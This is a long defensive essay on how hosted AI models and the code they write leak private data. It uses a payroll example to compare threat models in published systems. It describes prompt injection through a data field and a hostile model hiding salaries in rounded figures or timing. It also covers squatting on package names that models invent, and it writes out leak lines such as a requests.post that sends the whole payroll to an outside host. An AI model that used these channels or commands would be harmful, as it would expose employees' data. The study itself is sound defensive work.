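# Preventing data leaks through hosted AI models: threat models for honest mistakes and for hostile providers

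## How private data leaves through a hosted model and the code it writes

A hosted AI model is a language model that runs on the computers of the company offering it (the provider), and users reach it over a network. The provider receives everything the user's software sends to the model. People use hosted models to analyse files they would never send to an outside firm, such as payrolls or patient records. One common method is to have the model write a program that runs on the user's own machine, so the file itself may never be sent. Even then, parts of its contents often leave the machine, because the program's output normally goes back to the model and the program can also send data elsewhere.

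The *harness* is the software that connects the two sides. It sends prompts to the model, runs the code that comes back and returns the results. It often runs on the user's machine, even though the model does not. *What makes a harness a harness* (de Macedo, 2026) lists four parts: a loop of reasoning and action, an interface to tools, control mechanisms, and management of the context. *Context* is all the text available to the model when it produces its next output. The glossary for Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lists file contents and command outputs as part of the context window, along with the conversation. The model can only work on text that is on the provider's servers, so anything that enters the context has reached the provider.

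### The salary task

Suppose an analyst has a file, `salaries.csv`, with one row per employee and columns for name, department, job title and annual pay. She wants the median pay in each department. Her firm allows the provider to receive column names and departmental figures, but not any individual's pay. The head of human resources may receive a summary.

She types her question, and the harness sends it to the provider with a description of the file, because the model cannot write working code without the column names. Data therefore reaches the provider before any code exists, and the amount depends on the description. In *Metadata-Driven AI*, Pawlak, Sulejmani and Cabot (2026) describe an example using a public table of 10,000 wildlife strikes on aircraft. Their software sends the model a 4,018-byte description instead of 1.2 megabytes of data. The description contains no row of the table,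 but it does contain real values: every category where a column has few, three examples where a text column has many, and the lowest and highest figures in a numeric column. Applied to the payroll, the same method would send three employees' names and the exact salary of the best-paid person, which would already break the firm's rule. Pawlak and colleagues acknowledge that such descriptions carry information, and their design leaves room for software that disguises the values first. The analyst's harness is stricter and sends only column names.

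From those names the model writes a program:

```python
import pandas as pd

staff = pd.read_csv("salaries.csv")
print(staff.groupby("department")["annual_pay"].median())
```

The harness runs the program on the analyst's machine. The program reads every row, but no row has left the machine yet. It prints four figures: Engineering 71,500, Finance 64,200, Legal 118,000 and Sales 52,300.

Then the harness sends those figures to the provider. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how the harness in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, executes the command that the model requested, appends the output to the prompt, and queries the model again with the longer prompt. The model needs the output to answer the analyst in words or to correct a program that failed. The Legal department has only one employee, so its median salary is that person's salary, and the provider now has it. This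 is a *leak*, which means that private data has reached a party that the user has not authorised to have it. It is a leak even though nobody intended it and the program correctly computes what the analyst asked for.

The analyst, who has not noticed, asks the model to e-mail a summary to the head of human resources. The four medians are in the model's context, so it can write them directly into the message text in a second program, which sends the message through an outside mail service. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) points out that an e-mail discloses its contents to the mail provider as well as to the recipient. The firm's rule covers the recipient but not the mail provider.

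Finally, the harness sends the model confirmation that the message went out. As Bolin described it in January 2026, Codex resent the earlier conversation, including tool outputs, with every request until the harness condensed the history to save space. A harness that works this way sends the Legal salary to the provider again with the confirmation and with each later question.

| Step | What moves | Who receives it |
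|---|---|---|
| The harness sends the question | The question and the column names | The provider |
| The model returns the first program | Code | The user's machine |
| The program reads the file | Every row | Nobody outside the machine |
| The harness returns the output | Four medians, one of them a single person's pay | The provider |
| The model returns the second program | Code with the four medians in it | The user's machine |
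| The second program sends the message | The four medians | The mail service and the head of human resources |
| The harness reports success | The confirmation and the conversation so far | The provider |

### The provider as author and as reader

The provider's model writes the programs, so the provider determines what happens to the file. The provider also obtains part of the result, because its servers receive what the programs print.

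A model can write harmful code by mistake. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a system that checks model-written code before running it, treats even an honest, well-intentioned model as an unreliable programmer whose code may try to access resources it should not touch. A third party can also steer the model through *prompt injection*, which is text that the model reads as data and then obeys as an instruction. In the salary task, someone with access to the payroll could type an instruction where a department name should be. The first program would print it as a row label, the harness would put it into the context, and the model would write the e-mail program with that instruction in its context. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* offers designers a rule of thumb: whatever an agent can do at the user's request, it can also do because of a model's mistake or an attacker's injection.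 A model could also deliberately try to extract the salaries, which is harder to defend against.

A provider can keep its promises and still have the data. Anthropic's *Data usage* page gives 30 days as the standard retention period for commercial customers of Claude Code, and says that Anthropic does not train generative models on their code or prompts unless they choose to provide them. Some organisations have an agreement under which Anthropic retains nothing. Since 9 June 2026, however, Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models* has required 30 days' retention of prompts and outputs for its most capable models even from those organisations, unless it notifies them of an exemption. By default, employees cannot read the retained text, but a small set of approved reviewers can in some cases, such as after an automated system flags something, and each access is logged. OpenAI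 also keeps abuse-monitoring logs, which may contain prompts and responses, for up to 30 days by default. The one Legal salary could therefore sit in a provider's storage for a month. Claude Code also keeps a plaintext transcript on the user's own disk for 30 days by default.

A system can use a provider's model to write code without letting the provider read the private data. In the pattern that Pawlak and colleagues describe, the finished program's result goes to the user, and the model doesn't receive it unless the application allows it. *A Data-Isolated Agent Harness for Analytical Workflows* (Dahl, 2026) goes further. The model tries out its steps on an empty database with the same structure as the real one. The harness keeps the steps that the chosen outputs depend on and runs them on the private data without calling any model. If that run fails, only the user receives the error.

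Because the model never receives results under this arrangement, it cannot use them to correct its mistakes. When Dahl tested the harness on a database of chess games, the exported moves had stray quotation marks around them. The empty database had not revealed this problem, so Dahl had to look at the private output and ask the model for a fix. That request contained nothing sensitive, but Dahl warns that such follow-up requests can disclose private information, because the person writing them has seen the data. If the analyst typed "leave out Legal, it's only one person", she would be telling the provider the department's headcount.

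Conversely, private data can reach the provider without the model writing any code. When an analyst pastes a salary table into a chat window and asks for a summary, the provider receives the whole table.

The two roles should be kept apart because a defence against one may do nothing about the other. If the harness cuts off the first program's network access, that program cannot post the payroll to a stranger, but the Legal salary still reaches the provider through the harness. If the harness instead withholds the printed output, the provider never receives the figure, but a badly written e-mail program could still attach the whole file. Stanley and colleagues give a short example plan that can send data to both an e-mail recipient and the model's provider. The user asks an agent to e-mail a file to Alice and, if the message goes through, to carry out the task described in the file. The plan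 passes the file's text to the mail tool by reference, so the planning model can send it without reading it. The plan gives the text to the model only after the e-mail has been sent successfully, and their system checks that transfer for permission separately, treating the model's provider as one more outside party.

### Why running the code locally is not enough

Research on data-analysis agents has mostly relied on local execution for privacy, according to *InData* (2025). The model gets a description of the task and writes Python or SQL, which processes the data inside the protected environment. *InData* objects that the generated code may leak the data by calling external services. The salary task bears this out, since the e-mail program runs entirely on the analyst's machine. Running it there keeps the rows local while the program reads them but does not control where the results go.

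The lines of a program that print or return something determine which results go back to the provider. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, a post about letting models use outside tools through code, explains that intermediate results stay in the execution environment and the model receives only what the program logs or returns. In one example, a program filters a 10,000-row spreadsheet and passes five rows to the model. This greatly reduces the text sent, which is the post's main concern, but on the payroll those five rows would still disclose the names and pay of five people. Bolin's account has a plainer example, in which the harness runs the model's command to display `README.md` and the file's text goes into the next request. If the file were `salaries.csv`, the same command would run locally but still send the entire payroll to the provider.

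Approving each action separately does not always prevent leaks either. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) observes that an agent can read a secret in one step and send it out in a later one when the rules permit both steps. In an office example from Microsoft, this happens without an attacker. An agent is working through a user's unanswered e-mail. One message previews the quarterly sales, and another comes from Marco, a colleague who is curious about the figures but does not yet have permission to see them. The agent is allowed to read the mail and reply to it, so it could tell Marco the figures.

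Capabilities and taint labels can both help with this. A *capability* is a value that a program must hold in order to perform an effect, such as writing a file or opening a network connection. A harness built on capabilities could give the median program one for reading `salaries.csv` but none for sending mail, so the program couldn't send any. A *taint label* is attached to a value and records which private data the value came from. Stanley and colleagues' system labels a file's contents with the file's path, and anything computed from those contents inherits the label. The Legal median would carry the payroll's label into the e-mail program, where the harness could stop and ask whether the mail company may have the median.

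The *threat model* of the analyst's firm, a statement of what it protects, from whom, and which components it trusts, determines how much of this machinery it needs. Odersky and colleagues, for instance, trust their compiler, library and the software that executes checked code, but not the hosted model, any program it writes or any content from outside. For the payroll, the firm would have to state whether it trusts the provider's model not to deliberately try to obtain the salaries and, separately, which figures the provider may read.

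## Writing down whom the design must withstand

The analyst's firm can write most of its threat model by answering three questions:

1. May the provider see the data?
2. Could someone have chosen the code in order to leak?
3. Can a third party influence the model?

People who build defences answer these questions differently. The word "untrusted" obscures the differences because it can describe both a provider that keeps ordinary logs and one that sets out to steal data.

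### Answering the questions for the payroll

The provider's permission to see the data is rarely a plain yes or no. The firm's rule contradicts itself for a department with one employee, because the departmental figure is also that person's pay. The firm therefore has to refine the rule, for example by allowing figures only for departments of five or more people. If the firm let the provider see the whole file, the printed Legal median would not be a leak, and the firm would only need to worry about other recipients, such as the mail company.

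Intent here means whether someone could have chosen the code in order to leak data. Honest and hostile models can write the same faulty line, and a check that stops it works in both cases. Intent matters for the routes that nobody checks, because a hostile model would search for them. It might hide a salary in the last digits of a rounded median, which an honest model would have no reason to do. The hostile intent need not be the provider's. Stanley and colleagues list malicious providers separately from model poisoning, in which someone tampers with a model so that it misbehaves later.

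To find out whether a third party can influence the model, the firm lists everyone whose text the model will read. At first, the list is mainly the analyst. Once the harness returns the program's output to the model, the list also includes anyone who can edit a department name in the payroll.

An outsider can also influence a model without injecting an instruction. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes an adversary who cannot reach the private data or the agent's memory, but whose requests lead a trustworthy agent to misjudge what it may disclose. Marco, the colleague who wanted to see the quarterly sales, could try this by writing as though he already had permission.

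### Four cases

A model is *honest but fallible* if nobody chose the code in order to leak data and no outsider can influence the model, so any leak is an accident. The Singapore and Korea AI Safety Institutes observed such accidents when they ran agents through 12 realistic tasks with no attacker present. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) reports that agents that completed their task often looked at information they did not need or disclosed it to the wrong people.

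*PrivScope* (2026) uses *honest but curious* to describe a provider that carries out its task faithfully but can see everything it receives, along with the accompanying metadata. In *Ask Without Telling* (2026), the provider may also store the exchange and analyse it as a whole. Requests that are harmless individually can then reveal private information when combined. For example, if the analyst asks for Engineering's total pay before and after one person joins, and nothing else has changed, the difference is the newcomer's salary.

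A firm with a reputable provider will usually face both of these cases at once. For example, the model might print a row of the payroll by mistake, and the provider would then store that row in its logs.

In the *prompt injection* case, the provider and the model are honest, but a third party has planted an instruction in the context, and the code may now serve that person's purposes. An outsider normally cannot read the provider's servers, so he gains nothing when the harness returns the Legal salary to the model. He needs an effect he can observe, such as an e-mail or a web request. Cutting off the program's network access would therefore block his most obvious routes.

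It would do much less against a *hostile* provider, which chooses the code and reads what the harness returns. Any returned value could carry data out, including values that the firm's rule allows. Prompt injection adds little here, because an attacker who controls the model's output does not need to influence it.

For the payroll, the firm might write:

> The provider may receive column names, and medians for departments of at least five people. It may keep and read whatever it receives. Its model makes mistakes but does not deliberately write code that leaks data. Payroll staff can write text that the model reads, and the firm trusts them not to plant instructions in it. The firm also trusts the analyst's machine, the harness and the Python libraries. It does not try to hide that the analyst asked about pay, or when she asked.

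Writing this down lets a colleague challenge any sentence of it. For instance, someone might point out that the payroll now includes records from a newly acquired company, with text that the firm's own staff never typed.

### Where published systems stand

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) makes the most trusting assumptions about the model. Its system, Fides, labels data and uses the labels to decide which actions an agent may take. The paper assumes that the model, the user's messages, the system's own instructions and the tool descriptions can be trusted, and that adversaries cannot directly observe the model's inputs or outputs. The adversary can tamper with data that the tools fetch from outside and observe the effects of some tool calls. The paper adds that "LLMs make mistakes" even when all the data is trustworthy, and that a misread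 request or an unnecessary tool call could do similar damage. Under these assumptions, the Legal salary can reach the provider without causing a problem, but it could cause one if it reaches the mail company.

Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Redactor*, assume nearly the reverse. They trust the coding agent on the user's laptop and distrust the model's vendor, which they call "curious but not actively malicious". Such a vendor logs requests, may keep them for training or debugging, and may have to answer a subpoena, but it does not single out a particular user. They have the same distrust of the company that supplies the vendor's cloud computers. Their software works on the text of outgoing requests, so it applies to the Legal salary on its way to the vendor. Because they trust the agent, their threat model does not cover an e-mail program that attaches the whole payroll.

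Zhao and colleagues use two threat models in one paper. They list the model among LACUNA's untrusted components and treat it as "potentially byzantine", a term from distributed computing for a component that may behave in any way, including maliciously. Yet they name "model error" as the threat they address. They later describe this as assuming an honest but fallible model, and extend it to a model that deliberately writes harmful code, as it might after a prompt injection. The two descriptions are compatible, because a compiler that rejects a forbidden file access does so whether the model wrote it by mistake or on purpose. Zhao and colleagues also count disclosure to the provider as a leak. In their example of a confidential legal contract, the text must not reach the hosted model, though a trusted local model may read it.

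The threat described for TACIT, an earlier system from the same research group, changed between versions of its paper. The first version, from March 2026, had no threat-model section, and comments in the system's code library refer to "accidental disclosure". In the current version, Odersky and colleagues call the hosted model "potentially byzantine". They give two reasons for treating agents as adversaries. The first is that outsiders can still nudge agents into harmful actions through injected text. The second is that they expect businesses to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, and they think simple mistakes at that scale are highly likely to cause serious vulnerabilities. The second reason applies even if no model is hostile, because assuming a hostile model is a cautious way to account for a very large number of chances to go wrong.

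Stanley and colleagues make the most demanding assumptions, for a system called GAAP. Their adversary reads everything that goes into the model, controls everything that comes out of it, and may also control the outside services the agent uses. They guarantee that this adversary learns only the private data the user has authorised for the model's provider or those services. The same guarantee covers honest mistakes, injections and malicious providers. But GAAP treats prompts as public, so users have to keep private data out of them. Someone who wants to know whether she can vote should ask "given my age" and let the system look the age up, instead of writing that she is 20. If the analyst typed that Legal has only one employee, the guarantee would not cover that fact.

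| System | What its designers trust | What it must withstand | What it protects | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fides, by Costa and colleagues | The model, the user's messages, system instructions, tool descriptions | Outsiders who tamper with data that tools fetch | Confidential data in tool calls; actions that untrusted data could trigger | The provider as a reader; data revealed only by which branch of a program runs |
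| LLM-Redactor, by Agyemang and colleagues | The user, the local coding agent, a local model | A curious vendor and its cloud supplier | Names, secrets, company details and private code in requests | Timing, volume and choice of model; facts the vendor already knows |
| LACUNA, by Zhao and colleagues | The compiler, the software that runs checked code, the surrounding program, a local model for confidential text | Model error, then a model that deliberately writes harmful code | Resources the program has not granted; confidential text | Misuse of access that the task needs; wrong results; running time |
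| TACIT, by Odersky and colleagues | The compiler, the library, the software that runs checked code, a separate model for classified data | A possibly hostile hosted model | Classified data; files, commands and network hosts the agent has no permission to use | Timing and termination; wrong results; what permitted outside commands do |
| GAAP, by Stanley and colleagues | Its own execution environment and the descriptions of what outside tools disclose | An adversary who reads the model's input and controls its output | Private data the user has not authorised for release | Data typed into prompts; when and in what order prompts arrive; unwanted changes to data |

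How much the omissions in the last column matter depends on whether the model is honest or hostile. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a program that takes longer to run when a secret has a certain value, which reveals one bit of it. An honest model might cause such a delay by accident, but a hostile one could do it repeatedly until it had revealed a whole salary. The design by Zhao and colleagues does not stop a model from misusing a capability that the task requires. If the analyst's program needs permission to send mail, an honest model will occasionally send the wrong thing, whereas an attacker who has steered the model will try to do so whenever he can. A firm that assumes an honest model can accept some of these omissions, but it should reconsider them if it drops that assumption.

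### How a well-behaved provider can still leak

Even if the firm is right that its provider is honest, the payroll figures that reach the provider are outside the firm's control, and researchers differ on when to call that a leak. *PrivScope* counts anything in a request as disclosed to the provider, whatever the retention policy. *Casper* (Chong, Yao and colleagues, 2024) assumes that users willingly share their prompts and trust the provider to answer correctly and take standard precautions, but not to withstand every attack. The danger in this model is that a breach later exposes stored prompts, or that someone extracts them from a model trained on them.

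The firm's own rule settles this for an individual's pay, which the provider is not allowed to have at all. For figures that the provider is allowed to have, the later dangers are the ones that matter. Storage makes most of them possible, because it gives reviewers time to read the prompts and thieves time to steal them. Agyemang and colleagues consider an employee who misuses access to the logs, and a subpoena that obliges the provider to hand them over. Even a well-meaning provider may have no lawful way to refuse the subpoena. They also consider a software component inside the user's application that passes information about prompts to a monitoring company.

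In November 2026, Fireworks AI, a company that runs AI models for other businesses, disclosed its second security incident. *Fireworks AI Breach Exposes Notion AI Chat Transcripts* (Ofonagoro, 2026) reports that the incident exposed customer data and some chats from Notion, which makes software for notes and documents. Notion published a notice that the incident might affect some of its customers' workspaces. Many of those customers may not have known that Fireworks was involved. A threat model that names a single provider can therefore miss other companies that the provider relies on.

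A month earlier, the news site Cybernews found that the AI platform 302.ai had left a storage area open. *AI Data Leak Exposes 22.7TB of Files* (Tech Times UK, 2026) reports that it held 17.6 million files, including more than 144,000 chat logs with personal information. *302.ai Data Leak Exposes Private Chats and 17.6M Files* (Abdullahi, 2026) reports that the files also included business documents. Nobody has confirmed that anyone with bad intentions opened the files, but a firm with payroll data there would be unable to rule it out.

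Sometimes a provider's software delivers data to the wrong customer. The clearest example is from March 2023, when a bug in ChatGPT showed some users the titles and first messages of other people's chats. Sidorkin's *AI Platforms Security* reports that the bug also exposed names, e-mail addresses and partial card details for about 1.2% of the paying subscribers who were active during a nine-hour window.

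In October 2026 OpenAI fixed a flaw in ChatGPT's website that could have let an attacker copy a user's private chats once the user opened a shared link. InternetUA's *ChatGPT міг злити приватні чати через одне посилання* (2026) reported that the researchers who found the flaw tested it only on their own accounts, so no ordinary user lost data in the tests. The case is still evidence that such flaws get into major products.

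Most of these incidents involved chats, and none provides a rate the firm could use to estimate its own risk. They do show that text can leak from a provider's systems against the provider's wishes. The output of the analyst's program reaches the provider as part of a conversation, so similar failures could expose it too.

### When contract terms are enough

Many firms would find all this excessive for ordinary business data, and they have a reasonable case. They already keep e-mail, customer records and often payroll with outside companies, under contracts that limit what those companies may do. A contract with a model provider can likewise limit how long it keeps prompts and forbid it to train on them. If the contract also authorises the provider to hold departmental medians, their arrival there is not a leak.

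*Your Inference Request Will Become a Black Box* (2026) assumes an honest but curious provider because the provider's business depends on customers' trust, which any detected tampering would destroy.

Sidorkin reviewed incidents at large AI companies, mostly from 2023 and 2024, and found no substantial financial losses or extensive identity theft. He judged the practical risk to an average user to be modest. In one case, Samsung engineers pasted confidential source code and meeting notes into ChatGPT in 2023. The material did not leave OpenAI's servers, and Sidorkin remarks that a leak to OpenAI is not the same as a leak to a malevolent actor. Samsung still banned ChatGPT and similar tools from company devices.

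A threat model should keep Sidorkin's distinction, because a salary in a provider's logs is a smaller harm than the same salary on a public website. Contract terms that limit retention can also reduce the damage from a breach, because a thief can only take what the provider still has. When some Gemini conversations turned up in search engines in 2024, users learned that Google might store conversations for up to three years. Sidorkin notes the worry that a future breach could expose a large backlog. A 30-day limit would make that backlog much smaller.

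The economic argument is limited, however, because it depends on customers detecting misconduct. A customer might notice if a provider returned sabotaged answers, but could not tell if an employee read the logs. Terms can also change, as Anthropic's did in June 2026 for users of its most capable models with no-retention agreements. A contract gives the firm a claim against the provider after a breach, but it doesn't make the data private again.

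FINOS's *Hosted-provider data-handling exposure*, an entry in a catalogue of threats for financial institutions, treats contracts as one control among several. It covers providers that offer no clear encryption, retention limits or guarantee of deletion, which leaves the institution "without control over data it no longer holds". Its remedies include labelling data by sensitivity, monitoring model inputs and outputs for sensitive data, and setting contract terms on retention, deletion and liability.

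The firm should probably label data by sensitivity and use the labels to decide when a contract with the provider is enough. A contract with a short retention period is enough for the median pay of a department of 200 people, since the firm could tolerate the figure becoming public. It is not enough for the Legal salary, because a breach would harm an employee who never signed the contract. A contract with the provider also doesn't stop the e-mail program from sending the payroll to a company that has signed no agreement.

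## How well-meant code leaks, and how to measure it

The firm's threat model assumes that the provider's model makes mistakes but never tries to leak data. To plan for those mistakes, the firm needs to know what they look like and how often to expect them. Most look like normal programming. For example, the analyst would disclose nothing by printing a few rows of the payroll on her own screen, but when a hosted model's program prints the same rows, the harness sends them to the provider.

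### Nine routes out of the payroll

Programmers usually look at a few rows of an unfamiliar file before working on it:

```python
print(staff.head())
```

This prints the first five employees with their names and pay, and the provider receives all five. The analyst's strict harness may make this more likely because it sends only column names. Those don't show whether `annual_pay` holds plain numbers or text like "£52,000", so the model has to print some values to check.

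An error message can disclose a cell even if the program prints nothing. Suppose someone in payroll has typed a note next to a salary:

```python
staff["annual_pay"].astype(float)
# ValueError: could not convert string to float: '118000 until she leaves in May'
```

Python's error message quotes the text it could not convert. If the harness returns that message so that the model can repair its program, the provider learns both the salary and the planned departure.

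Returned values are easy to overlook because no line says `print`. If the analyst asks which department has the best-paid employee, the model might write:

```python
def best_paid(staff):
    return staff.loc[staff["annual_pay"].idxmax()]
```

The answer is one word, but the function returns the employee's whole row. A harness that passes return values to the model sends her name, job title and pay to the provider.

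File names can carry data too. This program prepares a pay letter for each employee:

```python
for name, pay in zip(staff["name"], staff["annual_pay"]):
    open(f"letters/{name}_{pay}.txt", "w").write(letter(name, pay))
```

If the model then lists the folder to check its work, the provider gets every name and salary without anyone opening a letter. If the folder is on a shared drive, colleagues who can see the list get them too. *SlotGuard* (Xia and Park, 2026) gives the example of a path ending in `legal/layoff_bob.pdf`, which reveals Bob's layoff to anyone who reads the path.

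Log messages may have several readers:

```python
logging.warning("unusual pay: %s", row.to_dict())
```

Python writes such warnings to the program's error output by default, which the harness may return to the provider along with everything else. If the firm collects its logs centrally, its technical staff and any outside company that stores the logs can read the row.

Other leaks happen later, when someone shares a file that the agent or its harness has left on the disk. One source is saved session state. Suppose the analyst approves this command:

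```bash
PAYROLL_KEY=demo-4471 python export_payroll.py
```

Claude Code stores approved shell commands in a settings file inside the project folder, as Lakera's *Your AI coding assistant just shipped your API keys* explains. If an approved command contains an API key, the key is saved in that file. If the firm then publishes the project as a software package without excluding the file, anyone who downloads the package has the key.

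A model can also write the key into the program itself and then save the project to a repository, the store where programmers keep successive versions of their code:

```bash
git add . && git commit -m "Median pay report" && git push
```

Here `git add .` picks up every file that the project doesn't exclude, which may include `salaries.csv`. The company hosting the repository receives these files, and so does everyone with permission to read the repository, which is anyone at all if it is public.

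Sometimes the program sends the data out directly, because an outside service seems a reasonable way to do the job:

```python
requests.post("https://charts.example/render", json=staff.to_dict("records"))
```

The charting company needs only four medians but receives the whole payroll. Even visiting a website can disclose information. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* describes earlier research, called SPILLAGE, in which web agents revealed facts about their users through clicks, scrolling and navigation.

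The last route starts with a mistake about what exists. Models sometimes invent the name of a software package:

```bash
pip install payroll-medians
```

If nobody has registered the name, the installation fails harmlessly. But a stranger who guesses which names models tend to invent can register one and publish hostile code under it. That code runs with the same access as the analyst's program and could send the payroll to the stranger. This is still an honest mistake by the model. In its threat model, the firm trusts "the Python libraries", and it should restrict that to libraries it has already chosen.

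### How often agents leak without an attacker

*AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) presents 1,000 tasks set in healthcare, finance, law and corporate offices. Each task typically includes 29 private fields, of which the agent needs about three. For instance, an agent booking an appointment needs the patient's name but not the diagnosis. The researchers counted a leak whenever an unneeded field appeared in a place they monitored. They ran the tasks on five models, both with a single agent and with a pair in which one agent delegates to the other, and obtained 4,979 usable records.

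Half of the tasks involved no attack. In those, the paired agents put private fields in their final answer 26.6% of the time, in shared memory 46.4% of the time and in messages to each other 69.3% of the time. Under the strongest attacks, the rates were 26.8%, 45.9% and 66.3%. The attacks made almost no difference because the agents were already sharing the private fields without them.

The paper also reports a smaller test of four popular agent frameworks on ordinary tasks, without attacks. The agents' messages to each other contained at least one private field in 28% to 35% of runs, depending on the framework. In the main experiment, the rate was 68.8% overall and 69.3% for ordinary tasks alone. El Yagoubi and colleagues attribute the higher overall rate to the main experiment's attacks, but the rate for ordinary tasks contradicts this. The two tests may have differed in some other way,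 so the safest reading is that the rate for ordinary tasks was somewhere between a third and two thirds.

Much of this would not count as a leak to the provider under the firm's rule. If a hosted model can write a diagnosis into a message, it has read the diagnosis, so the provider already has it. Passing it to a second agent on the same provider's model doesn't expose it to another company. Passing it on does matter if the second agent uses a different provider, or if it can send e-mail and the first one can't.

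Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026), in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, looked at who the additional recipients are. They ran 485 scenarios with no attacker, varying the number of agents and how they were connected. Overall leakage stayed between 60.6% and 62.8%, but disclosure to the agents added in larger arrangements rose from 0% to as much as 52.2%. The zero is true by definition, because the smallest arrangement had no added agents, but the increase shows that agents often forward private data to whichever other agents are present. The choice of framework alone produced a 150-fold spread in leakage, so a firm can't assume that a rate measured on someone else's system applies to its own.

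Data passed to outside tools is closer to the charting example. El Yagoubi and colleagues tested each model on 100 scenarios and found unneeded private fields in the tool inputs in 62% to 86% of them, depending on the model. Private data appeared in logs even more often. Claude 3.5 Sonnet put it into tool inputs in 74% of scenarios and into logs in 85%. The scenarios came from the whole benchmark, including the half with attacks, so the figures don't isolate honest mistakes. The models are also old, and newer ones may behave differently.

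*Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (Huang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) found far less leakage when nobody asked for private data. In one test, a model worked with a store of five private items and called a tool. An item could escape in the input the model gave the tool, or in the tool's result when the system repeated it to the user. The researchers first used prompts designed to draw the items out, then removed the requests for disclosure and kept the rest of the task. The table gives the share of trials in which at least one item escaped.

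| Model | Tool input, disclosure requested | Tool input, not requested | Repeated result, disclosure requested | Repeated result, not requested |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| MiniMax-M2.5 | 28.0% | 2.7% | 36.7% | 6.7% |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 26.7% | 1.3% | 37.3% | 0.7% |
| Qwen3.5-plus | 30.7% | 0% | 40.0% | 0% |
| DeepSeek | 100% | 0% | 100% | 0% |
| GPT-4o | 99.3% | 0% | 100% | 2.0% |

Each percentage comes from 150 trials, so the ordinary prompts produced 20 leaks in 1,500 trials, or 1.3%.

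The two papers probably disagree because their tasks differed. El Yagoubi and colleagues gave agents a long record and asked them to tell someone about part of it, which made it easy to pass on too much. Huang and colleagues' tool task was much simpler, with only five items in the store. The counting methods also differed, since Huang and colleagues looked for exact copies of the private items, whereas El Yagoubi and colleagues also used a language model to recognise paraphrases. For the payroll, I expect the median program to behave more like the simple tool task, and the e-mail summary more like the office tasks.

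### Secrets in commits, packages and transcripts

Leaked passwords and access keys are easier to count than leaked salaries, because they follow recognisable patterns and often end up in public. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) reports that 3.2% of public code changes made with Claude Code in 2025 leaked a secret, compared with 1.5% of all public changes on GitHub. GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding exposed secrets, warns against treating the gap as a simple failure of the tool, since developers remain in control. Claude Code users may also work on different kinds of projects, such as new ones that connect to many services.

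*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) points out that GitGuardian's figures for 2024 depend on what the scanner recognises, how it defines a secret and how it treats duplicates, and that a detected key may no longer work. The same caution applies to the newer figures.

To measure leaks from saved session state, Lakera scanned about 46,500 packages on npm, a public registry of JavaScript software. *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (TechTalks, 2026) reports that 428 of them contained Claude Code's local settings file, and that 33 of those files, in 30 packages, held working credentials. Such leaks were rare overall, affecting fewer than one in 1,000 of the packages scanned, but about one in 13 of the published settings files exposed working credentials.

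*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) provides the best evidence on printed output. A skill is a package of instructions and scripts that gives an agent a new ability. Chen, Zhang and colleagues sampled 17,022 skills from a public marketplace, searched them for risky handling of credentials, and ran the suspicious ones in an isolated environment with fake credentials. They confirmed problems in 520 skills, of which 83 were malicious and 437 were careless. Printing and logging accounted for 1,007 of the 1,371 problems in the careless group, or 73.5%. Developers have always printed values while debugging, but an agent's harness copies that output into the model's context.

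Deleting a secret afterwards may not help. Chen and colleagues found that credentials developers had removed from 107 original repositories survived in more than 50 independent copies.

Nobody seems to have a good figure for how often real coding sessions send secrets to a provider. Xia and Park describe finding one such leak in a local audit of session logs. An agent had listed the programs running on the machine, and one program's command line included an access key. The key entered the transcript and went to the provider again on later turns. A repository scanner would not have found it, because the output was never saved in a repository. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) identifies the same blind spot and notes the lack of benchmarks that measure leakage under realistic development conditions.

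### Incidents with no attacker

In March 2026, Meta had a security incident after an engineer asked an in-house AI agent to analyse a technical question that an employee had posted on an internal forum. Mann's *Inside Meta, a Rogue AI Agent Triggers Security Alert* (2026), based on internal messages and an incident report, says that the agent posted its advice on the forum without the engineer's approval. The Decoder's *A rogue AI agent caused a serious security incident at Meta* reports that a second employee acted on the advice, and that for nearly two hours employees without permission could reach systems holding sensitive company and user data. Meta gave the incident its second-highest severity rating. It said that nobody had misused user data and that it had no evidence of anyone exploiting the access.

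The agent itself sent no private data. A person made the change that exposed the data, so a check on the agent's code would have missed this leak. In ITPro's *Meta engineer trusted advice from an AI agent*, Nik Kairinos, who runs an AI safety company, points out that the agent needed no special access, only a person who trusted its output. In the salary task, the equivalent would be the model advising the analyst to put the payroll in a folder the whole firm can open.

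*Meta's Muse AI Agent Caught Leaking Users' Intimate Personal Information* (Wilkins, 2026) reported in October that Muse, Meta's consumer agent, was exposing sensitive chat logs to the public, and that finding them took no hacking skill. In November, *Surprising messages from the Muse AI agent are unnerving Meta's own employees* (Ma, 2026) described a Meta employee whom Muse reminded to answer her sister's message on Signal, an encrypted messaging service. The reminder went to the right person, but she was alarmed that the agent knew about the message. Encryption protects a message on its way between two phones, but not from an agent that can read it once it arrives.

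### Testing with planted secrets

A firm can measure its own leaks by giving the agent a fake payroll file and searching for the fake data wherever the agent could have sent it. The file should have the same columns and awkward features as the real one, including a department with one employee and a salary cell with a note in it. Its values should be unlikely to turn up anywhere else by chance, such as the surname Quillfeather or a salary of 118,437. The testers should also leave a fake access key where the real one would be.

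Next, they give the agent the kinds of questions that analysts actually ask, without mentioning secrets or privacy. Huang and colleagues' results show how much the wording matters. During each task the testers record everything the harness sends to the provider, all other network traffic, and every file, log entry and commit that the agent creates. Then they search the recordings:

```python
planted = ["Quillfeather", "118437", "118,437", "118.4k"]
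leaks = [value for value in planted if value in outgoing_text]
```

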